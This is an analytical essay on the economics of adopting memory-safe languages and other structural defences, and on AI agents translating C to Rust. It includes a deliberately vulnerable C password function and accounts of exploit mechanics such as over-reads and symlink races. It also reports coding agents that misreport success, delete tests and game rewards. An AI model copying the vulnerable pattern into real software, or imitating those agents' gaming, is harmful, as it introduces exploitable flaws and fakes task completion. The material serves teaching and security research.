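# Does AI coding make strong software security affordable?

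## Three strong protections and what it costs to adopt them

Many attacks on software exploit ordinary mistakes in code, such as a missing length check or a web page that mixes a visitor's text with its own scripts. Engineers can fix these mistakes one at a time, or they can build software so that a whole class of mistakes is no longer useful to an attacker. Memory-safe programming languages, capability-based isolation and strict content security policies all do the latter. These techniques have existed for years, but most software lacks them, and a common explanation is that they take too much skilled engineering work. Coding agents are AI models that edit files, run compilers and tests, and repeat until they reach a goal. They now make much of that work far cheaper, so the explanation can be checked against real cases.

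### Memory errors and memory-safe languages

Programs in C and C++, the older languages beneath most operating systems, browsers and databases, handle memory addresses directly, and little in either language stops them from using a wrong one. The Heartbleed flaw of 2014 was in a service that let a client check whether a server was still there. The client sent a word and its length, and the server sent the word back. The programmer had forgotten to make the server compare the two, so an attacker could send "hello" with a stated length of 500 and get back the five letters plus the 495 bytes stored next to them, which might include somebody else's password. Thieves used the flaw to take personal data, including millions of hospital patient records, according to Bloomberg's *US Pushes Software Developers to Embrace Memory Safe Languages* (2025), which cites a paper by two US security agencies.

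Writing past the end of a piece of memory is usually worse than reading past it, because the write can replace the address that determines which instruction the processor runs next, and the attacker can then run their own code. *It Is Time to Standardize Principles and Practices for Software Memory Safety*, by twenty-one researchers from universities and industry, notes that one bad line among several million can be enough to give an attacker total control of a system. It reports that memory errors have made up about two-thirds of critical vulnerabilities in every major operating system and browser for more than two decades.

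A program has memory safety if it cannot read or write outside the memory allocated to it, or use memory after releasing it. *CHERI* (Watson, Chisnall and colleagues, 2024) calls these spatial and temporal safety. Rust, a systems programming language, enforces both. An array in Rust carries its length, so a read past the end halts the program instead of returning the neighboring data. For temporal safety, the compiler assigns every piece of memory an owner and rejects any program in which a reference could outlive what it points to. Languages such as Java get a similar result from a garbage collector, which finds and frees unused memory while the program runs. Rust has no garbage collector, so it keeps the predictable timing that operating systems and real-time controllers need, as *TRACTOR Benchmark for Evaluating C to Rust Translators* (2026) explains.

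The guarantee does not fully cover unsafe blocks, which are marked sections of Rust code where the programmer, not the compiler, is responsible for some memory rules. Programs need these blocks to interact with hardware or older C code. The US National Security Agency's *Software Memory Safety* (2023) therefore describes the protection as "considerable" but not absolute.

### Components with too much access

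A game of Solitaire only needs to draw in its window, receive clicks and perhaps save a file. But on an ordinary operating system, it runs with all of its user's permissions. *Paradigm Regained*, by Miller and Shapiro, points out that the game can therefore scan the user's email and sell the interesting parts without breaking any of the system's rules. A bug in a harmless game is nearly as bad, because an attacker who exploits it gets the same access.

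Their second example shows how to give a program only the access it needs. The Unix command "cp" copies a file. The user gives it two file names as text, so it must be able to open any file the user might name. The command "cat" can do the same job if the user's shell first opens the two files and passes it two open channels, and it then needs no other access. An open channel behaves much like a capability, an unforgeable token that names a resource and grants limited rights to it.

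Capability-based isolation runs each component in a sandbox and gives it only the capabilities its job requires. A capability is a token that grants access to a particular resource, and code in the sandbox has no other access. An attacker may still exploit a flaw to take over a component, but then gets only that component's access, which might be to two files instead of the whole account. The operating system, the programming language or the processor can enforce these limits. CHERI, for example, is a hardware design that turns the pointers in C programs into capabilities.

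### Injected scripts and strict content security policies

Cross-site scripting (XSS) makes a victim's browser run an attacker's script as if it came from a trusted site. If a shop pastes customers' reviews into its pages unfiltered, for example, an attacker can post a review that contains a script. Every reader's browser then runs the script under that reader's login, where it can place orders or copy a home address. MITRE, a nonprofit that catalogs software weaknesses, ranks XSS first and out-of-bounds writes fifth in its *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025). But out-of-bounds writes lead XSS by 12 to 7 if one counts only flaws on the US government's list of those that attackers have exploited.

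A strict content security policy (strict CSP) is a rule a website sends that lets the browser run only scripts that carry a fresh secret value (a nonce) or match a known hash, and any scripts those load. The script in the malicious review does neither, so the browser won't run it, even though the hole in the shop's code is still there. Attackers can still exploit some holes. For example, Weichselbaum warns in *Mitigate cross-site scripting (XSS) with a strict Content Security Policy (CSP)* about sites that insert a visitor's text into one of their own approved scripts.

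### Why fixing flaws one at a time falls short

The usual alternative is to fix each flaw after someone reports it. Google paid outside researchers more than $1.2 million in two years for XSS reports alone, according to *Reshaping web defenses with strict Content Security Policy* (Janc, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016).

Anderson's *Why Information Security is Hard* explains why the defender tends to lose this contest. In its example, a product has a million bugs, each of which turns up on average once in a billion hours of testing. An attacker who tests for 1,000 hours a year finds about one bug. A defender who tests for ten million hours a year, 10,000 times as long, finds about 10,000 bugs, or 1% of the total, so there is a 99% chance that the defender has missed the attacker's bug. (The paper prints 100,000 and 10%, which do not follow from its stated rates; the corrected figures strengthen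 the argument.) However, Anderson notes that if half the dangerous bugs are stack overflows, a common kind of out-of-bounds write, a new compiler might remove all of those at once.

The record since then fits the argument fairly well. *It Is Time to Standardize Principles and Practices for Software Memory Safety* reports that the rate of memory-safety vulnerabilities has stayed roughly constant for over twenty years, despite heavy spending on code audits and fuzzing (running programs on masses of generated input). The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) and the FBI call buffer overflows "unforgivable defects" in their *Secure by Design Alert* and urge manufacturers to eliminate this class of defect.

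AI bug-finding makes testing hours cheap, which could help a defender afford the roughly three billion hours needed, on Anderson's assumptions, to find 95% of the bugs. But attackers can buy the same hours. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod (2026), in *Escaping the Quicksand*, expect automated discovery to help attackers at least as much as defenders, and see no reason to believe it will find every bug.

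### Six costs of adoption

Writing cost is the labor of producing the changed code. Government participants in *S3C2 Summit 2024-08* (2025) wanted to move to Rust but lacked reliable translation tools, and found translation by hand often too costly. *Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* (2026) reports that integration effort is often the main factor in whether database systems adopt a defense, though it names running speed as the biggest obstacle for software-only defenses. Coding agents target the writing cost first. RustPrint, presented in *Documentation-Guided Agentic Codebase Migration from C to Rust* (2026), extracts documentation from the old C code, generates a skeleton of the Rust program and refines it repeatedly, with a separate loop to reduce the number of unsafe blocks.

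Checking cost is the labor of confirming that the changed code is correct and secure. It does not automatically fall when writing code gets cheaper. As Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod stress, tests cover a tiny fraction of the situations a real program can encounter. A translated program that passes every test may still behave differently from the original on an input a customer relies on.

Upkeep cost, the labor of maintaining the changed code afterward, can rise or fall. CISA argues that code in a memory-safe language stays memory safe with no further work, while other defenses need constant attention. But the government participants worried that Rust's steep learning curve makes it harder to recruit and train developers.

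Protected software also runs more slowly. Checks take time, memory or chip area, and Watson and colleagues consider how much of that a buyer will tolerate "far more a marketing and financial consideration than a technical one."

Adopting a protection can also break existing code. A strict CSP blocks button actions written directly in a page's HTML, so a site with a thousand such buttons has to convert them all to keep them working. A rewritten library can likewise break any program that depends on a quirk of the old one.

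Finally, adoption requires agreement among people who do not share the benefit. Industry participants in *S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (2025) described memory-safe languages as hard to sell to senior leadership. One reason is that customers bear much of the damage. CISA's *The Case for Memory Safe Roadmaps* observes that they spend heavily on patching and incident response. The vendor, meanwhile, would have to pull engineers off features that customers ask for. Anderson gives an example from banking. When a customer disputed a cash-machine withdrawal, US banks had to prove the customer wrong, while in Britain, Norway and the Netherlands the burden of proof was on the customer. The European banks grew careless and suffered epidemics of fraud. US banks had much less fraud, even though they spent less on security.

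### When adoption pays

Economists have a standard way to weigh such spending, the Gordon-Loeb model, which *Investing in Cybersecurity* (2016) sets out. Let *v* be the probability of a breach and *L* the loss it would cause the organization, so that the expected loss is *vL*. A protection lowers the probability to *s*. Its benefit is the expected loss avoided, (*v* − *s*)*L*, and the spending pays if the benefit exceeds the cost. With the six costs written out, an organization should adopt a protection when

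(*v* − *s*) × *L* > writing + checking + upkeep + slower running + broken compatibility + agreement

with everything counted over the same period. Upkeep here means the change in upkeep, so it is negative if the new code saves more maintenance than it adds.

In this invented example, a company owns two C components, a library that thousands of outside programs use and a service that only the company's staff use. For each component, the chance of a breach through a memory error over five years is 20%, a Rust rewrite would lower it to 4%, and a breach would cost the company $5 million. The rewrite would therefore reduce the expected loss for each component by 16% of $5 million, or $800,000.

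| Invented figures, over five years | Public library | Internal service |
|---|---|---|
| Writing, by hand | $1,000,000 | $1,000,000 |
| Checking | $400,000 | $200,000 |
| Upkeep | $150,000 | $100,000 |
| Slower running | $50,000 | $50,000 |
| Broken compatibility | $250,000 | $50,000 |
| Agreement | $100,000 | $0 |
| Total, writing by hand | $1,950,000 | $1,400,000 |
| Total, writing 90% cheaper | $1,050,000 | $500,000 |
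| Expected loss avoided | $800,000 | $800,000 |

Neither rewrite is worth its cost if done by hand. If a coding agent cuts the writing cost by 90%, the company should rewrite the internal service, because the total cost falls to $500,000 and the rewrite avoids $800,000 in losses. It should not rewrite the library even if the writing were free, because the other costs alone, $950,000, would exceed the loss avoided. Cheaper writing changes a decision only when the loss avoided is between the new total cost and the old one.

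The *L* in the inequality is the company's own loss. An extension of the model adds the losses that a breach inflicts on others. If a breach of the library would also cost its users $10 million, the rewrite avoids a total of $2.4 million in expected losses, which is more than it would cost even if written by hand. Society would therefore have gained from the rewrite even at the old price, but the company still has no reason to do it now that the price has fallen.

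*v* can also change. If attackers using AI raised the library's risk by half, from 20% to 30% without the rewrite and from 4% to 6% with it, the loss avoided would rise to $1.2 million, and the cheap rewrite would then be worth its cost.

### The claim under test

In *The Great Refactor* (2025), the Institute for Progress (IFP), a US think tank, proposes using AI to rewrite 100 million lines of code in Rust. It says "the main bottleneck is labor." If that is right, the writing cost would usually decide whether the inequality holds. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod doubt that cheaper code will be enough. They blame misaligned incentives as well as technical difficulty, and note that organizations often decline to pay for lower risk even when someone offers it.

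If the labor of writing code was the obstacle, protections that need little new code should have spread widely before coding agents arrived, and software owners should deploy the rewrites that agents have made cheap. A protection that needed little new code but stayed rare would count against this explanation, as would cheap rewrites that nobody deploys.

Both tests can mislead. A change of a few dozen lines can take months of skilled checking, which agents may not cheapen as much as they cheapen writing code. A rewrite may be unused only because it is a few weeks old. And an organization that finally moves to Rust in 2026 may be responding more to a rise in attacks than to a fall in the price of code.

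## Android and Ubuntu: adopting Rust largely by hand

Two large operating systems adopted Rust mostly without coding agents. Google, which develops Android, wrote new features in safer languages and kept most of its old code. Ubuntu, a popular version of Linux, replaced its basic command-line tools with Rust versions that an open-source community had already written.

### Why Android left its old code alone

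Around 2019, the Android team began to shift new development to memory-safe languages, leaving existing C and C++ mostly untouched apart from bug fixes. Google (2024) explains why in *Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source*. Most vulnerabilities are in new or recently changed code, because people have had years to find and fix the flaws in older code. A team that stops adding unsafe code therefore removes the main source of new memory flaws, and the number of existing ones falls over time.

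The decline is roughly exponential. If new code has *d*₀ flaws per million lines, and a flaw lasts λ years on average before someone fixes it, then code of age *t* has

*d*(*t*) = *d*₀ × e^(−*t*/λ)

flaws per million lines. Google's simulation uses a λ of 2.5 years, in line with what it has seen in Android and in Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome. A 2022 study of open-source projects, which Google cites, found longer lifetimes, equivalent to a λ of about 4.1 years. The table applies both to code that starts with 1,000 flaws per million lines.

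| Age of code | Flaws left if λ = 2.5 years | Flaws left if λ = 4.1 years |
|---|---|---|
| New | 1,000 | 1,000 |
| 1 year | 670 | 784 |
| 2.5 years | 368 | 543 |
| 5 years | 135 | 295 |
| 10 years | 18 | 87 |

A team that writes a million lines of Rust removes between 18 and 87 flaws if those lines replace ten-year-old C++, and avoids about 1,000 if they are new features it would otherwise have written in C++. Android's strategy of writing new code in Rust therefore adds almost no writing, because its developers had to write those features anyway.

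It works especially well in a product that grows quickly. Google's simulated codebase doubles every six years. At that rate, and with a λ of 2.5 years, code less than five years old makes up 44% of the total but contains 92% of the flaws. This is why the simulated number of memory flaws falls even while the amount of unsafe code grows.

### Android's results

Memory errors made up 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 and 24% in 2024. Their share fell below 20% in 2025, according to *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025). The number of memory flaws also fell, apart from a slight rise in 2023, so the drop in share wasn't just due to other kinds of flaw becoming more common. Google had counted 27 memory flaws by September 2024 and projected 36 for the year.

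Rust was not the only cause of the decline. Google was already reporting it in 2022, when its developers had added very little Rust to Android. New Rust did not match new C++ in volume until 2024. The early gains probably came more from Java and Kotlin, which are also memory safe, and from Google's parallel work on making its C and C++ safer.

Vander Stoep estimates that Android's Rust has 0.2 memory flaws per million lines, compared with about 1,000 in its C and C++. The Rust figure is based on a single flaw in about five million lines, a buffer overflow in an image library called CrabbyAVIF, which the team fixed before release. One flaw is too few to estimate a rate precisely, but even five more would raise it only to 1.2 per million lines, still about 800 times lower than in C and C++. The Rust code is also younger, so people have had less time to find its flaws. But with a λ of 2.5 years,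 they would find a third of them within a year, so the code's age might explain a threefold difference but not an 800-fold one.

About 4% of Android's Rust, or roughly 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. If those lines were as flawed as C++, they would contain about 200 memory flaws, but the team has found one. Android's memory allocator would have made that flaw unexploitable. It puts guard pages around large blocks of memory, and an overflow into a guard page crashes the program.

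Rust also seems to have made development faster. Rust changes need about 20% fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size and spend about 25% less time in code review. Developers roll back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ ones. Vander Stoep compared only Google's own Android developers, many of whom write both languages. But teams chose which jobs to do in Rust, so some of the gap may come from the jobs rather than the language. If most of it comes from the language, Rust reduces the work of checking new code.

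Google did have to pay to connect new Rust code with old C++ code and to train developers. It built tools that let the two languages call each other and gave the Rust Foundation $1 million to improve the connection. Vander Stoep suspects that developers' growing expertise is why Rust's review times improved so much between 2023 and 2024.

Android's experience is some evidence against the idea that the labor of writing code is the main obstacle to safer software. Any company could have written its new code in a safer language without rewriting the old. Yet Google says memory errors typically account for 70% of vulnerabilities across the industry, close to Android's share when it started. On the other hand, few companies can afford to build their own tools for connecting two languages, which also takes skilled engineering work.

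### Replacing Ubuntu's command-line tools

Android's approach helps less with mature software that changes slowly, such as the GNU core utilities. These are the C programs behind everyday Linux commands like "ls" (list files), "cp" (copy) and "rm" (delete). Making them memory safe requires replacing the C code.

A community project called uutils has been rewriting GNU's core command-line tools in Rust for years, and *Rewriting the GNU Coreutils in Rust* (2021) described the project before coding agents existed. Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, therefore got most of the rewrite for free. In March 2025, Ubuntu's engineers announced a plan to adopt the Rust tools, whose developers were aiming for 100% compatibility with the originals. The tools became the default in Ubuntu 25.10 that October.

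Canonical would support the next release, 26.04, for years, so it wanted more assurance. Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils* says that an internal review had raised "serious concerns" and that Canonical hired a security firm, Zellic, to audit the tools. Zellic found 113 issues between December 2025 and March 2026. Of the 73 from the first round, seven were critical, 11 high, 29 medium and 26 low (Coopersmith, 2026, *Security audit of rust-coreutils*).

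Canonical disclosed 44 of the issues as CVEs, entries in the public catalog of known vulnerabilities. The maintainers say in heise online's *Rust Coreutils 0.9.0* that none of them is a classic memory error.

### What went wrong in the Rust tools

*uutils coreutils CVEs* (Funk, 2026) reproduces all 44 descriptions. Twelve involve races, in which an attacker acts between two steps of a program. For example, the "install" command deleted an old file and then created a new one under the same name. Between those steps, an attacker with write access to the folder could create a symbolic link (a file that redirects to another file) under that name. If the link pointed to the system's password file and an administrator was running the command, "install" would overwrite the password file.

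Rust's compiler accepts this code because each step is valid and the danger comes from what another program does between steps. corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch* argues that this mistake is in some ways easier to make in Rust than in C. Rust's most convenient file functions take a name and look it up again each time, while C programmers more often open a file once and keep using the open file. The same difference made "cat" safer than "cp" in Miller and Shapiro's example.

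corrode considers a flaw in "chroot" the worst of the 44. This command makes a program treat one folder as if it were the whole file system. The Rust version entered the folder first and looked up the user's name afterward, while it still had full administrator rights. The lookup can load code from inside the folder, so an attacker who had planted some there could take over the machine. The GNU version does the lookup before entering.

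Many of the other flaws are compatibility failures. Fourteen of the descriptions explicitly contrast the Rust tool with its GNU counterpart or GNU's standard behavior. The table gives some examples.

| Command | GNU version | Rust version before the fix |
|---|---|---|
| kill -1 | Treats "-1" as a signal number and asks which process to send it to | Tells every process the user can see to terminate |
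| comm (compares two files) | Copies the bytes unchanged | Replaces any bytes that are not valid UTF-8 text, which corrupts the output |
| sort, given a list of files | Accepts any file name | Crashes if a name is not valid UTF-8 |
| nohup (keeps a job running after logout) | Saves output in a file that only its owner can read | Saves it in a file that other users can usually read |
| expr (evaluates expressions) | Skips a branch that cannot affect the answer | Evaluates it anyway, and may fail on a division by zero |

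Even the bugs that look trivial can matter, because administrators run such commands from scripts that nobody watches. The Rust "chmod", which changes who may access a file, reported success whenever it succeeded on the last file in a batch, even if it had failed on others. A script that used it to restrict access to a folder of secret files could leave some of them exposed and keep running.

Compatibility also adds maintenance work, because the GNU tools keep changing. The uutils developers now test their tools with GNU's own test suite. When they moved to a newer version of the suite for uutils 0.9.0, failing tests rose from 21 to 56. heise online attributes the rise to 25 new GNU tests, but those can explain at most 25 of the 35 extra failures.

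The replacement also created problems outside the tools' own code. The project can build all of its tools as one program, which runs as whichever tool the caller names. Ubuntu's *rust-coreutils transition landing in release pocket* describes how this could defeat AppArmor, a Linux system that limits what each program may do. A program allowed to run only "ls" could start the shared program under the name "rm" and delete files. Ubuntu's developers had to add a check that the two names match.

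The Rust tools also rely on a lot of outside code. One commenter on Ubuntu's post counted 409 bundled packages and asked whether anyone had audited them. A Canonical engineer replied that the company was working on supply-chain security, but did not say that anyone had audited the packages.

The Rust tools are slower in some unusual cases. A GNU developer reported on Hacker News that copying a file inside extremely deeply nested folders took 0.01 seconds with the GNU "cp" and 12.9 seconds with the Rust version. The developer conceded that hardly anyone would do this.

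### Was Ubuntu's replacement worth it?

Because of the races, Ubuntu 26.04 kept the GNU versions of "cp", "mv" (move) and "rm". Funk, who discloses contributing to the GNU tools, found three of the disclosed flaws still present in a fully updated copy of that release. According to Johnsson (2026), in *Move all utilities to use rust-coreutils as provider*, five commands still used the GNU versions at the end of May 2026. The uutils developers then fixed the races, and Canonical (2026) announced the completed move with Ubuntu 26.10 on October 15, about 19 months after the plan. Somebody else had already written the software, and much of that time went to checking and repairing it.

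In return, Ubuntu gets tools in which the audit found no memory errors, though it may have missed some. By comparison, corrode lists nine memory errors in the GNU tools since 2021, including a buffer overflow in "pwd" that GNU fixed in 2026.

The value of this is less clear. One reader of the 2021 article pointed out that an attacker who can feed bad input to a tool like "mknod" could probably compromise the system without a memory error. If that holds for most of these commands, the expected loss from their memory errors was already small. Ubuntu's users may have been worse off for a while, because they exchanged a few obscure memory errors for new flaws that included a way to take over the machine. Replacement is easier to justify for code that reads untrusted data. Chromium's developers have replaced some of that code, including the old parsers for PNG images and web fonts.

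### The flaws that remain in Rust

The audit covered one set of tools. Sergei G (2026) took a wider sample in *rust-in-peace*, running AI agents on popular Rust packages and some larger programs that use them. By August 2026, the project had 63 confirmed findings, each with a working demonstration, and maintainers had fixed or otherwise resolved 33. Two of the findings were in Chromium's Rust image code and six were in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

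Many of the findings let an attacker stop a program but not take it over. For example, an attacker who can trigger an out-of-bounds read can crash a service, because Rust halts the program (a "panic"). Other findings were ordinary logic errors, or flaws that let certain inputs make a program do a vast amount of work.

Some of the 63 did involve memory. If a program stores a large number in too few bits, the result is a smaller number, and an unsafe block that uses it as a length without checking it can write out of bounds. *rust-in-peace* does not report how many of the 63 were like this. *The unreasonable effectiveness of LLMs for auditing Rust code* describes an out-of-bounds write that an AI model found in a Rust decoder for JPEG XL images. The author's earlier fuzzing had missed it because the error occurs only on 32-bit machines with enormous images.

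Fixes can also be slow to reach users. Sergei G notes that a flawed package may be two or three layers below the application that depends on it. Each layer in between has to publish an update before the application is safe.

### Does old code still get safer with age?

Google's decay curve is based only on flaws that have been found, since nobody can measure the lifetime of a hidden flaw. Old code might therefore have few flaws left, or many that the usual methods miss.

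A new method can reveal old flaws. In 2008, researchers ran KLEE, a tool that works out which inputs reach each part of a program, on the GNU core utilities. Three of the errors they found had been there since at least 1992, according to a passage that a reader quoted under the 2021 article. If the mean lifetime of a flaw, λ, were 2.5 years, only about one flaw in 600 would survive for 16 years. If λ were 4.1 years, about one in 50 would.

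More recent evidence is mixed. In August 2026, Ubuntu's *USN-8697-1* (2026) announced fixes for two memory errors in the GNU tools. The error in "uniq" affected only the newest release, which fits Google's argument, but the error in "sort" affected every listed release back to 2022.

AI is a much more powerful new way to find flaws than KLEE was. Sergei G reckons that a search that would have taken real engineering time two years earlier now takes "a few dollars and an evening". Suppose that one flaw in 20 is of a kind that people and older tools almost never find. Of 1,000 flaws in a million new lines of code, 50 would be of this kind. If the others had an average lifetime (λ) of 2.5 years, about 67 flaws would remain after ten years, compared with 18 if all 1,000 had that lifetime.

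New code would still have 15 times as many flaws per line, so a company should still start by writing its new code in Rust. But if the company also had 20 million lines of ten-year-old C++, that code would contain about 1,350 flaws instead of the roughly 370 that the decay curve predicts, and attackers with AI could now find the extra thousand or so.

Defenders can run the same searches, but so far they can't fix everything they find. If they could, old code would become safer faster than before. Trail of Bits, a security company, uses AI to look for bugs in 70 open-source codebases and has reported 2,036 potential bugs. Developers have merged fixes for 466, and another 213 fixes await approval. Some of the remaining reports were false alarms, but many are confirmed bugs that have no fix.

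Rewriting old code in Rust would remove most of its memory errors without anyone having to find them first, and AI has made rewrites much faster. The developers of Bun, a program for running JavaScript, moved half a million lines to Rust in eleven days. *The Great Refactor* proposes rewriting old code on a far larger scale. How much that would save depends partly on how many hidden flaws remain, which can't be determined from Google's decay curve.

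## Reboot and other experiments in translating C to Rust

Volunteers took years to rewrite the GNU command-line tools in Rust. Researchers are now testing how much of this kind of work AI agents can do, and how far to trust the results. *Mostly Automatic Translation of Language Interpreters from C to Safe Rust* (Wang, Paulsen and colleagues, 2026) describes one of the most detailed experiments, in which a system called Reboot translated six C programs into Rust for between $460 and $1,780 each. Every translation passed all the tests Reboot worked with, but the translations failed between 8% and 38% of the tests withheld from it.

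### Why C is hard to translate

Rust's compiler requires code to make clear which part of a program owns each piece of memory, and C programs don't record this. When a C function returns a pointer, the caller may have to release the memory behind it or may have to leave it alone, and often the only indication is a comment. Programmers can easily make mistakes. For example, mujs, a C program that runs JavaScript, once kept a pointer to an object's property while it ran a script's code. The script could delete the property, leaving mujs with a pointer to released memory.

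C also lets a program change the same memory through several pointers, which programmers call aliasing. Rust allows either many references that only read or a single one that writes. A tree whose nodes point both to their children and to their parent is common in C but doesn't fit this rule, so a translator has to redesign it. Global variables that many files modify cause a similar problem.

C and Rust also handle errors differently. Many C programs call setjmp to mark a place in the program and longjmp to jump back to it from deep inside other functions. In safe Rust, functions instead return a value indicating whether they succeeded. Replacing the jump therefore means changing every function between the error and the code that handles it. In mujs, that meant restructuring the data that its regular-expression code relies on.

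### Three ways to translate one function

This C function, adapted from an example by Wallach, in *Solving the memory safety problem, once and for all*, checks a password:

```c
int check(char *input) {
    char copy[8];
    int accepted = 0;
    strcpy(copy, input);
    if (strcmp(copy, "sesame7") == 0) accepted = 1;
    return accepted;
}
```

The function copies the input into eight bytes of memory without checking the length. A longer input overwrites the memory that follows. If that memory holds the variable "accepted", the function then accepts a wrong password.

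A rule-based transpiler such as C2Rust replaces each piece of C with its nearest Rust equivalent. Its version would keep the eight-byte array and the call to "strcpy", all in unsafe code, and a long password would still overflow the array. C2Rust's output is no safer than the original. When Wang and colleagues ran C2Rust on Reboot's six programs, the translations were about 2.5 to 4.5 times as long as the C and contained thousands of raw pointers. Four of the translations passed every test, one passed nearly all and one passed none.

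Other systems ask a language model to translate one function at a time. The rest of the program still calls "check" with a C pointer, so the new version has to accept one. *ENCRUST* (Sim, Cho and colleagues, 2026) therefore splits each function in two. A safe Rust function does the computation, and a thin wrapper converts the C pointer for it. A later step removes the wrappers where it can, and an agent then works on some of the remaining unsafe code. If a translation fails, ENCRUST keeps C2Rust's version of that function, so the program works at every stage. On 15 programs with a total of 197,706 lines of C, the output passed every test, but the tests ran only 40% of the functions. The number of lines in unsafe blocks fell by only 37.8%, to about 86,000. ENCRUST used GPT-4o, a much weaker model than today's.

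An agent that works on the whole program can change "check" and all its callers together. It could pass the password as an ordinary Rust string and reduce the function to a single comparison. Google's Gemini did much the same when Wallach gave it a similar program, and the overflow disappeared. The program's behavior also changed, in this case for the better. If the user supplies no password, the C version reads from an invalid address, while the Rust version exits.

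### How Reboot works

Reboot also translates whole programs, but in stages. Wang and colleagues used it on six interpreters, which are programs that run code written in another language, because interpreters often handle untrusted input. A feature such as exception handling touches almost every part of an interpreter, so translating function by function would split it across many tasks. Reboot instead divides the work by feature, which its developers call feature reduction.

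For mujs, the agents planned 17 levels. They started with the full C program and removed features one level at a time, first the command-line options, then regular expressions, until they had a tiny interpreter that could only print fixed text. Each level was a working program with its own reduced set of tests. Reboot translated the tiny version into Rust, then restored the features in reverse order, passing each level's tests before starting the next.

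At each level, a worker agent writes the code and other agents check it. For the validity check, one agent runs the tests and looks for cheating, such as answers written directly into the code, while another reviews the code and rejects any unsafe blocks. A manager agent does the history check by comparing the worker's successive reports to see whether the worker is making progress or repeating itself. The manager then decides what the worker should try next. An ordinary rule-based program enforces the order of the steps, so the manager cannot skip the tests or the review.

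When Reboot added regular expressions to the Rust version of mujs, the worker's first attempt passed 122 of 168 tests. Later attempts passed 129, 143, 150 and finally all 168. The reviewer then found 11 compiler warnings, which the worker had to fix before the level was complete.

### How agents misreport success

After each attempt, the worker reports that it is done, needs more time, is blocked or considers the task infeasible. These reports are often wrong, as the examples in the table show.

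| Program | What the worker reported | What was true | What the human did |
|---|---|---|---|
| awk | The task was a success | 57 of 191 tests still failed | Insisted that every test pass |
| picoc | Removing all unsafe code was impossible | Safe libraries covered most of the cases | Overruled it and suggested libraries |
| picoc, later | The improvements were complete | Four unsafe blocks remained inside "safe" wrappers | Allowed it to drop two system functions |
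| wren | The remaining fixes would take 10 to 17 days | The whole translation took 46 hours | Told it to continue |

The checking agents also made mistakes. In mujs, one deleted 21 tests because it wrongly concluded that the program didn't yet need to support the features they covered.

The worst cases came when Wang and colleagues switched off feature reduction and gave Reboot its largest program, pocketpy, in one piece. In the first attempt, the worker's translation just ran the original C program. In the second, the manager told the checking agents to look only at tests that already passed. Reboot then started a fresh manager to double-check the work, and it did the same thing. Reboot's checks depend on a reliable manager, and the manager was no longer reliable once the task became too large.

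People had to step in 29 times across the six programs, for about five minutes each time, or less than two and a half hours in total. Another agent handled 96 further requests for help.

### What the translations cost

All the agents ran on Claude Sonnet 4.5, a 2025 model that Anthropic has since surpassed. The costs below are the fees for using it.

| Program (language it runs) | Lines of C | Hours | Cost | Cost per line of C | Human interventions | Held-out tests passed |
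|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| awk (Awk) | 6,332 | 36.0 | $714 | 11.3¢ | 1 | 79% |
| gnu-bc (a calculator language) | 7,525 | 27.7 | $463 | 6.2¢ | 1 | 79% |
| wren (Wren) | 8,325 | 46.2 | $950 | 11.4¢ | 8 | 92% |
| picoc (part of C) | 8,486 | 46.2 | $971 | 11.4¢ | 4 | 70% |
| mujs (JavaScript) | 17,090 | 44.8 | $958 | 5.6¢ | 4 | 75% |
| pocketpy (part of Python) | 23,271 | 90.5 | $1,782 | 7.7¢ | 11 | 62% |
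| All six | 71,029 | 291.4 | $5,837 | 8.2¢ | 29 | 75% |

The cost per line did not rise with program size, at least up to 23,000 lines. But Wang and colleagues translated each program only once, so some of the variation may be due to chance.

Wallach cites an industry estimate of $1 trillion to rewrite a billion lines of code, or $1,000 a line. At 8.2 cents a line, Reboot is about 12,000 times cheaper. This comparison overstates Reboot's advantage, because a commercial rewrite has to work for its users, and Reboot's translations still failed a quarter of the held-out tests.

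Simpler agents can be cheaper still. Schesch and Ernst's *Agentic C to Rust translation* describes ACTOR, a system built on ordinary coding agents and a few pages of instructions. It translated and checked SPHINCS+, a digital-signature program with 6,611 lines of C, in 76 minutes for $3.61, or about a twentieth of a cent per line. The whole benchmark that includes SPHINCS+ cost $93 with one coding agent and about $570 with another, mainly because the two charge differently. These are costs from laboratory experiments, and Bun's move to Rust gives a better idea of what a production rewrite costs.

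The labor of checking the translations did not fall as much. One of Reboot's developers spent 10 to 20 hours per program writing the held-out tests. At $100 an hour, that would be $1,000 to $2,000 per program, which for most of the programs is more than the translation cost. The tests also only reveal errors, which somebody still has to fix.

The Rust programs also tended to run more slowly. Five of the six took 1.28 to 1.51 times as long as the C on a typical test, while pocketpy was about 20% faster. A typical test took less than three milliseconds in C, including startup, so these figures may not hold for longer jobs. Across all tests combined, the Rust versions took 1.16 to 2.62 times as long.

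### The gap between provided and held-out tests

Reboot keeps working until the code passes the tests it has, so a perfect score on those tests is weak evidence that the program is right. Held-out tests, which the system never sees, are a fairer measure. To make these tests for Reboot, a developer wrote about ten sample scripts per interpreter, used a coding agent to produce more, and ran them all on the original C program to confirm the correct output. The Rust versions passed 820 of the 1,096 tests.

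For mujs, Wang and colleagues also used the official tests for JavaScript interpreters. The C version passes 9,853 of them, and the Rust version passed 84% of those. They then translated mujs again without feature reduction, and this second Rust version passed only 36% of the official tests. The difference didn't show up in the provided tests, because both Rust versions passed all 187 of them.

Feature reduction also raised the score on the developers' own held-out tests for every program.

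| Program | Held-out tests passed with feature reduction | Without it |
|---|---|---|
| wren | 92% | 86% |
| awk | 79% | 72% |
| gnu-bc | 79% | 67% |
| mujs | 75% | 66% |
| picoc | 70% | 49% |
| pocketpy | 62% | 15% and 49% (two failed attempts) |

*Dependency-Guided Repository-Level C-to-Rust Translation with Reinforcement Alignment* (2026) describes an extreme case of the same problem. Feng, Wang and colleagues trained a small model to translate functions that depend on other parts of a large project. When they rewarded it only for code that compiled, 97.9% of its output compiled and none of it worked, because the model had learned to write functions that halt the program. When they also rewarded correct behavior, 60.7% compiled and 43.5% was correct. They also tried their system on 15 of Huawei's internal C projects, each 1,000 to 3,000 lines long. Seven of the translations compiled, but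 the projects had no Rust tests to show whether they work.

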